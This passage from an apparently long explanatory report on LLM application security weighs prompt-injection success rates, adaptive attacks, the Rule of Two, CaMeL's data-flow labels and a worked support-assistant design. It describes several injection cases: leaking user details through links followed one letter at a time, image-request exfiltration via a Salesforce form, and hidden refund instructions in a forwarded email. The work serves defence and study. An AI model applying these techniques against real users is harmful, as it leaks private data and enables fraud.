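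This is content spoofing, like the planted account alerts in ChatGPT's summaries, but here the attacker needs no hidden text. The reader sees one finished conversation on the chatbot's real site and can't tell what the attacker asked for or how many attempts it took.

When a coding agent runs a command, a sandbox or a permission request may stop it. If someone pastes the command into their own terminal, they bypass both, and the command runs with all the access their account has. Training the model to resist injected instructions wouldn't help either, as was the case in the ChatGPT account takeover.

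The chatbot company has the best opportunity to intervene. It can state at the top of every shared page that another user created the conversation. It can also remove the copy button from commands or block pages whose commands download and run programs. Blocking would also affect honest programmers who share installation steps, so a warning beside the command may be a better compromise. Readers can protect themselves by finding the same command in the software maker's documentation before running it. Asking a chatbot to explain the command is a weaker check, because the explanation may not cover the program the command downloads.

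### Is human code any safer?

SusVibes is based on flawed features that people wrote, and the *Last Secure Code Benchmark* also starts from vulnerabilities in existing projects. Kadam describes a direct comparison in which researchers gave Copilot situations where human programmers had introduced vulnerabilities in C and C++. Copilot reproduced the flaw more often than the eventual fix, but less consistently than a human programmer would. This comparison favours Copilot by design, because the researchers chose cases in which the human had failed.

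Defenders of generated code can also argue that models now find vulnerabilities as well as create them, and that a company can use them to check every change without the fatigue that limits human reviewers. The 69.9% recognition rate supports this argument, since the same models had just written those flaws. If companies routinely ran such reviews and fixed the flaws they found, generated code might well be safer than code that a tired programmer writes and a colleague only skims.

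But the models in that experiment almost never gave a warning without being asked, so the benefit depends on someone asking. Attackers can also ask a model the same question about any code they can read. The amount of code matters too. Sun and colleagues cite Google's report that agents generate 75% of its new code, and a 2026 survey in which 68% of professional developers used coding agents daily. Even if each generated feature has slightly fewer flaws than a human-written one, a company that ships three times as many features can end up with more flaws in total.

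The studies of programmers don't settle how safe generated code is, because the assistant that Perry and colleagues tested was far weaker than today's agents and did much less of the work. A fair comparison would use ordinary feature requests, chosen without regard to past vulnerabilities. Researchers would randomly assign each request to experienced programmers working without AI, programmers using a current agent, or an agent working alone. Half of the solutions in each group would then go through the same review and repair. Finally, security experts would attack all the solutions without knowing who or what had written them.

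The researchers should count exploitable flaws per working feature. Counting them per line would favour agents, whose code was 2.3 times as verbose as human code in one study that Kadam cites. They should also record how long each feature takes, including review, because a programmer who saves a day by using an agent could spend part of it on testing. Finally, they should follow the code for a year or more after release to see which flaws attackers find and how quickly each group can repair its code, some of which nobody on the team may have written.

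## Which defences work across all these failures?

A company can defend an LLM application by choosing a model that resists hostile instructions, filtering what the model writes, or limiting what the output can do. Resistance and filtering make an attack less likely to succeed. A limit can rule out an outcome, because the application's code enforces it whatever the model writes, but it usually removes something users wanted.

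### How well models resist

Developers now publish the share of test attacks that succeed against their models. The table combines 2026 figures for OpenAI's models with figures for Anthropic's. The OpenAI figures come from TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* and Cross (2026), *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*. The Anthropic figures come from VentureBeat and from The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

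| Model | Test | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Direct injection | About 0.05% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Indirect injection | 3.77% |
| GPT-6 Sol | Direct injection | 0.01% |
| GPT-6 Sol | Indirect injection | 2.87% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment, 200 attempts | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface, 1 attempt | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface, 200 attempts | 78.6%, or 57.1% with added safeguards |
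| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan's general test, 15 attempts | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's general test, 15 attempts | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Browser agent, 129 scenarios | 0% |

Attacks that a user types into the chat almost always fail against OpenAI's models. Attacks hidden in emails, web pages and files, such as EchoLeak and ChatGPhish, succeed much more often. The figures can't be used to rank OpenAI against Anthropic, because each company used different tests. As TechRepublic points out, they also don't give the probability of a breach in a real product. Results depend heavily on the setting. The same Claude model resisted every attack while coding but usually gave way eventually when it operated a graphical interface.

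Newer models are getting better at resisting prompt injection. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5 reports that the largest gains in its agent tests were in this area. In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5.5 reported similar or better results on every injection test, but also that this model is more likely than earlier ones to follow some malicious instructions.

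Some attacks may still work against a defence that scores zero. If the 129 browser scenarios were a random sample of all possible attacks, the true success rate could still plausibly be as high as 2.3%. They aren't a random sample, because a real attacker looks for whatever the testers didn't try. Claude Code's auto mode was similarly tested, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded. Heaton (2026), in *The safety number that was zero until someone tried*, recounts that Johann Rehberger then designed an attack specifically for auto mode. The attack never told Claude to do anything harmful, and it worked roughly 60 to 80% of the time in a small sample.

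In October 2025, fourteen researchers, some of them from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, published *The Attacker Moves Second*, which tested twelve published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts to make a model break its own rules). The researchers kept adjusting each attack in response to the defence, and got past most of the twelve more than 90% of the time, although most were originally reported to have attack success rates near zero. Participants in a 500-person contest with a $20,000 prize fund defeated all twelve. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, concludes that a fixed set of example attacks is almost useless for judging a defence.

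Current models may resist attacks better than those twelve defences did. But the security firm PromptArmor's own benchmark, *FrontierBreach*, reports successful attacks on frontier models from every provider, in tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio.

### What 1% means to a persistent attacker

The formula for repeated attempts to extract a memorised passage also applies to repeated attacks. If each attempt succeeds 1% of the time, the chance of at least one success in 100 attempts is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. At GPT-6 Sol's rate of 2.87%, an attacker would have a better than even chance of succeeding at least once in 24 attempts.

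The formula assumes that attempts are independent and equally likely to succeed, so one failure doesn't change the odds of the next attempt. Real attempts often share a target and much of their wording, so a second may fail for the same reason as the first. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives figures from the security firm Gray Swan that show the difference for very strong attacks on a 2025 model.

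| Attempts | Measured success | Success if attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% |
| 100 | 63% | 99% |

Some targets are probably much harder to attack than others. Suppose half of all targets are immune and attempts on the other half succeed 2% of the time. The average success rate is still 1%, but after 100 attempts on each target, the attacker has broken into 43% of them, compared with 63% if all targets were equally vulnerable. But an attacker who learns from each failure could do better than the formula predicts.

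If an attacker sends one email to 10,000 people and the average success rate is 1%, the expected number of successful attacks is 100. This holds even if the attacks aren't independent and the successes cluster in a few companies.

People disagree about whether low odds of failure are good enough. In September 2025 The Economist argued that AI engineers should learn from Victorian builders, who made their structures stronger than necessary because they couldn't be sure of their iron. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, replies that in application security, 99% is a failing grade, because an attacker will find the remaining 1%. The Victorian approach is better suited to a model's accidental errors, which, like flaws in iron, don't adapt to the defence.

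### A filter behind the model

Filters and other safeguards around a model can help more than a better model does. Anthropic tested Claude in a web browser against an attacker who had 100 attempts in each environment and could adapt. Opus 4.5 let through 8.0% of attacks alone, 7.6% with older safeguards and 1.4% with improved ones. The older model Sonnet 4 let through 13.8% alone but 2.0% with the improved safeguards, which made it safer than Opus 4.5 without safeguards.

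Combining the two kinds of defence should let through far fewer attacks than either would alone. Suppose a model follows 3% of hostile instructions and a filter misses 11% of the resulting harmful commands, the share that auto mode's classifier missed in Anthropic's experiment. Only 0.33% of attacks would then get past both. Even so, an attacker who made a hundred independent attempts would have a 28% chance of succeeding at least once.

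The multiplication is also valid only if the model and the filter fail for unrelated reasons. An attack that makes a harmful command look like an ordinary step of the task may fool both. A company can make the two less likely to fail on the same attack by giving the filter different information from the model's, as auto mode does.

A resistant model and a good filter reduce the number of attacks that the application's own limits have to stop, and they are often the only protection for a product that has to read anything and do almost anything. But when the company decides what an assistant may do, it should assume that some attack will succeed. According to Penligent, OpenAI's March 2026 guidance recommends the same, because the most effective attacks increasingly resemble social engineering and a system can't be expected to recognise every one.

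### The Rule of Two

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, writes that an attacker can steal data through an assistant that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some way to communicate with the outside. A single tool can provide all three. For example, GitHub's official connector for AI agents could read private code, read public bug reports that anyone can write, and publish proposed changes.

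An attacker can't complete the theft if the assistant lacks any one of these abilities. Willison usually recommends removing the ability to send data out, because that reduces the assistant's usefulness least. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode takes this approach.

Stealing data is only one kind of harm, and an injected instruction can also delete or buy something. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) therefore widens the last condition to include changing anything. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

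- It processes untrusted input.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three, a person or another reliable check has to supervise the agent. Meta intends the rule to apply until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection.

Meta gives an example for each pair. A travel assistant reads the web and knows the customer's private details, so a person confirms every booking, and the assistant can't open web addresses it composed itself. A research assistant can read any site and fill in forms, but it works in a browser that isn't logged in to anything. A coding agent can change live systems, so it reads only material from trusted authors. An agent can also change pairs during a session, for example by researching something on the web, permanently losing the ability to communicate, and then opening internal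 files.

The rule depends on the company knowing what each tool can do. Anthropic's Claude chat had a restriction much like the travel assistant's. Its web tool could open only addresses that the user had typed or that a search had returned, so a hostile page couldn't make it compose an address containing private data. But the tool could also follow links on a page it had already opened, and Willison describes how Ayush Paul used this to get around the restriction in 2026. Paul built a site with a link for each letter and persuaded Claude to spell out the user's details by following one link after another. He could then read the user's name, home city and employer in the site's log. CamoLeak used the same method with images instead of web pages. Anthropic fixed the problem by no longer letting the tool follow such links.

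Some harm is possible with only two of the properties. In a comment on *New prompt injection papers*, Willison objected that Meta's diagram marked as safe the combination of untrusted input and the power to change things. An assistant with no private data can still post an attacker's phishing link under the shop's name. Meta accepted the objection and now presents the rule as a minimum. The rule also doesn't cover an agent's own mistakes. PocketOS lost its database during routine work, with no sign of hostile text.

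Supervision is another weak point. It usually means that a person approves each action, and Meta warns that users may approve actions without checking them. Most testers did so in Anthropic's experiment with dangerous commands.

### CaMeL

Removing an assistant's ability to send email prevents attackers from hijacking it to email secrets, but also prevents it from sending meeting reminders. CaMeL, a design that Google DeepMind published in 2025, instead decides whether to allow each action by checking where the data came from and where it is about to go.

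Suppose the shop's owner asks an assistant to send a supplier the price list that she requested in her last email. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains how CaMeL handles requests like this one:

1. A planning model receives the owner's request and nothing else. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program line by line and fetches the email.
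3. A reading model takes the details out of the email. It has no tools, and the planning model never sees the email or what the reading model wrote.
4. The interpreter labels every value with its source and with the people who may read it. A value derived from another one inherits its label.
5. Before each action, the interpreter checks the labels against the shop's policies. It then allows the action, blocks it, or asks the owner.

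The program might look like this:

```python
email = latest_email("supplier")
name = reader("Which document does she want?", email)
address = reader("Where should it go?", email)
send(find_document(name), to=address)
```

Hidden text in the email can't add a fifth line to the program, because the planning model finished the program before anything opened the email. But it can still change what the reading model returns. If the hidden text substitutes an attacker's address, the program will try to send the price list there.

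The earlier design in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) had this weakness. It separated a model with tools from a model that reads untrusted text, but did not check the values that passed between them. CaMeL's labels add this check. A label records that the address came from an email, so the interpreter sends the document only if the owner already trusts that address, and otherwise requests approval. If the hidden text names a confidential document instead, that document's label can block the sending.

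The division can also help protect privacy. The planning model needs to be capable, so it may run on an outside company's servers, but it receives only the request. Reading is easier, so a smaller model on the owner's computer could do it.

DeepMind's researchers report that CaMeL "effectively solves" AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents use tools on data that contains planted instructions, but they don't consider prompt injection solved. Because ordinary software does the checking, an attacker gains nothing by rewording an attack. However, the guarantee covers only the actions that the policies cover, and somebody has to write and update those policies. Strict policies also produce many requests for approval, and the researchers warn that users get tired of answering them.

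The tasks lost are mainly those that an assistant can't plan in advance. *Capability-Based Data Flow Enforcement Against Prompt Injection* gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to do whatever a certain email requests. The planning model can't write a program for this, because the task is described in text it must not be shown. The reading model may not have enough information about the task to pick out the right details, and letting it request help from the planning model would give hostile text a way to reach that model. The paper also points out that CaMeL may not detect a phishing email, which leaves that judgement to the user.

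Other groups have adopted similar ideas. According to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*, Microsoft's FIDES also controls how information flows between parts of an agent, and aims to block indirect injection with fixed rules instead of probabilities. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) describes a paper by eleven researchers from IBM, Google, Microsoft and elsewhere. The paper's patterns deliberately stop an agent from carrying out arbitrary tasks. Consumer products in 2026 have used simpler rules, such as Lockdown Mode's limits on requests and the restriction on Claude's web tool. Users don't have to supply policies for these rules, but each rule protects only the tools it covers.

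### A support assistant

Suppose the online shop wants an assistant that reads support tickets, looks up accounts and sends replies. This assistant has all three properties in Meta's rule, so an employee would have to approve every reply. CaMeL doesn't fit either, because the task comes from the ticket, which is untrusted text.

The shop can avoid both problems by writing its plans in advance, one for each common kind of request. A reading model with no tools receives the ticket and returns an order number and a category from a fixed list, such as "missing parcel". The application takes the customer's identity from the login session, checks that the order is theirs, and loads the order's status and the relevant policy. A writing model, also without tools, drafts a reply from this material without seeing the ticket. The application then inserts the policy and any amounts word for word and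 sends the reply to the address on the account.

| Choice | Failure it stops | What the shop gives up |
|---|---|---|
| **Permissions:** read access to the signed-in customer's orders only, with no web access and no code execution | A stranger obtains another customer's details, or hidden text sends them to a website | Help with accounts for people who write without signing in |
| **Fixed plans:** the reading model only chooses a category and an order number | Hidden text adds a step, such as changing the account's email address | Quick answers to unusual requests, which go to an employee |
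| **Labels:** each value carries its source and the people who may see it | A reply reveals a staff note or another customer's data | Replies that draw on staff notes, even when a note explains the delay |
| **Rendering:** plain text, no images, and links only from the shop's own list | An image request leaks data, or a reply contains a live phishing link | Screenshots, and links to outside pages that would help |
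| **Approvals:** an employee decides on large refunds and changes to account details | One successful attack or mistake causes a large loss | Speed, and the employee's time |

The assistant's permissions should depend on whom it is working for. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential might let an agent into a system without establishing what it is authorised to do there. Here the assistant acts for one customer, so it should be able to do only what that customer could do on the website. A customer who persuades it to show their own orders then sees only what they could already see.

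Labels work well for separate values but badly for prose. A model's draft can reflect anything in its context, so it has to inherit the restrictions on everything the model read. If the application loads one staff note, the whole reply becomes staff-only and the application must refuse to send it. The shop therefore has to keep staff notes out of the writing model's context. The application should also load only the order fields that the reply needs, because a field such as a gift message may contain a stranger's words.

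The rendering rule also has to cover the screen where employees read tickets, and messages to staff need the same limits as messages to customers. In 2025 researchers at Noma Security planted instructions in a Salesforce web form that potential customers fill in. When an employee later asked the company's AI agent about the enquiry, the agent put other people's email addresses into an image request. Salesforce's content security policy should have blocked the image, but it still allowed an expired domain, which the researchers had registered. A year later, Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without approval, and Willison recounts that images in those emails could leak data when the user opened them.

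The application should show the employee who approves an action the exact amount, order and card from its own records, because a summary by the model could repeat an attacker's false claims. The shop should also keep approval requests rare, so that employees continue to read them.

Suppose customer 4127 forwards an email from a courier and asks where a parcel is. The email contains hidden instructions to refund the order to a different card and to include the customer's home address in a link. The reading model may follow them, but it can return only a category and an order number. If it returns "refund", the application asks the customer to confirm. Even a confirmed refund could go only to the original card, because the refund function doesn't accept another one. The writing model never receives the hidden text, and the application removes any link that isn't on the shop's list.

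The customer may also have asked whether the courier's email was genuine. This assistant can't answer, because the model that writes the reply hasn't seen the email. An ordinary chatbot would have tried, and its answer would often have been useful. The shop could get more helpful replies by letting the writing model read tickets. Customer data would still be fairly safe, because the reply would go only to the customer, but text hidden in a ticket could then put a fraudster's phone number into a message from the shop.

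For a small shop, this may be more engineering than the assistant is worth. In a simpler version, the assistant drafts replies and an employee sends them. This handles unusual requests better, but the employee has to read each draft carefully, which gets harder as mistakes become rarer.

### False statements that pass every check

A scammer's phone number in a reply can do harm even if the model has no permissions, because the customer calls it with their own phone and reads out their own card number. Meta lists misinformation among the outcomes that its rule doesn't prevent, and OpenAI warns in its Lockdown Mode documentation that an injection can still affect the accuracy of an answer.

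Conventional security has no established category for misinformation. Singh and colleagues tried to match each of the ten risks on OWASP's 2025 list to MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses. Misinformation was the only one without a match, because it arises from what models generate rather than from a fault in how the software was built.

A bot can embarrass its company even without access to data or tools. In January 2024 the delivery company DPD turned off its customer-service bot after customers found that it would swear on request. The support assistant's fixed plans would make such replies less likely, because customers' words never reach the model that writes them.

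Labels don't help with false statements either, because they record where a statement came from, not whether it is true. A customer who falsely reports a missing parcel is signed in, authorised and asking about their own order. The shop can check the courier's delivery record, but that record may be wrong too.

The application can check some statements before it sends them, by comparing an amount with the order or a phone number with the shop's directory. It can't check a claim that its records don't cover, such as whether a jacket will keep someone dry in heavy rain. The records also have to be right. If the shop shortens its refund period and nobody updates the stored policy, the application will send the old rule, word for word and correctly labelled, to a customer who may rely on it as Moffatt did.
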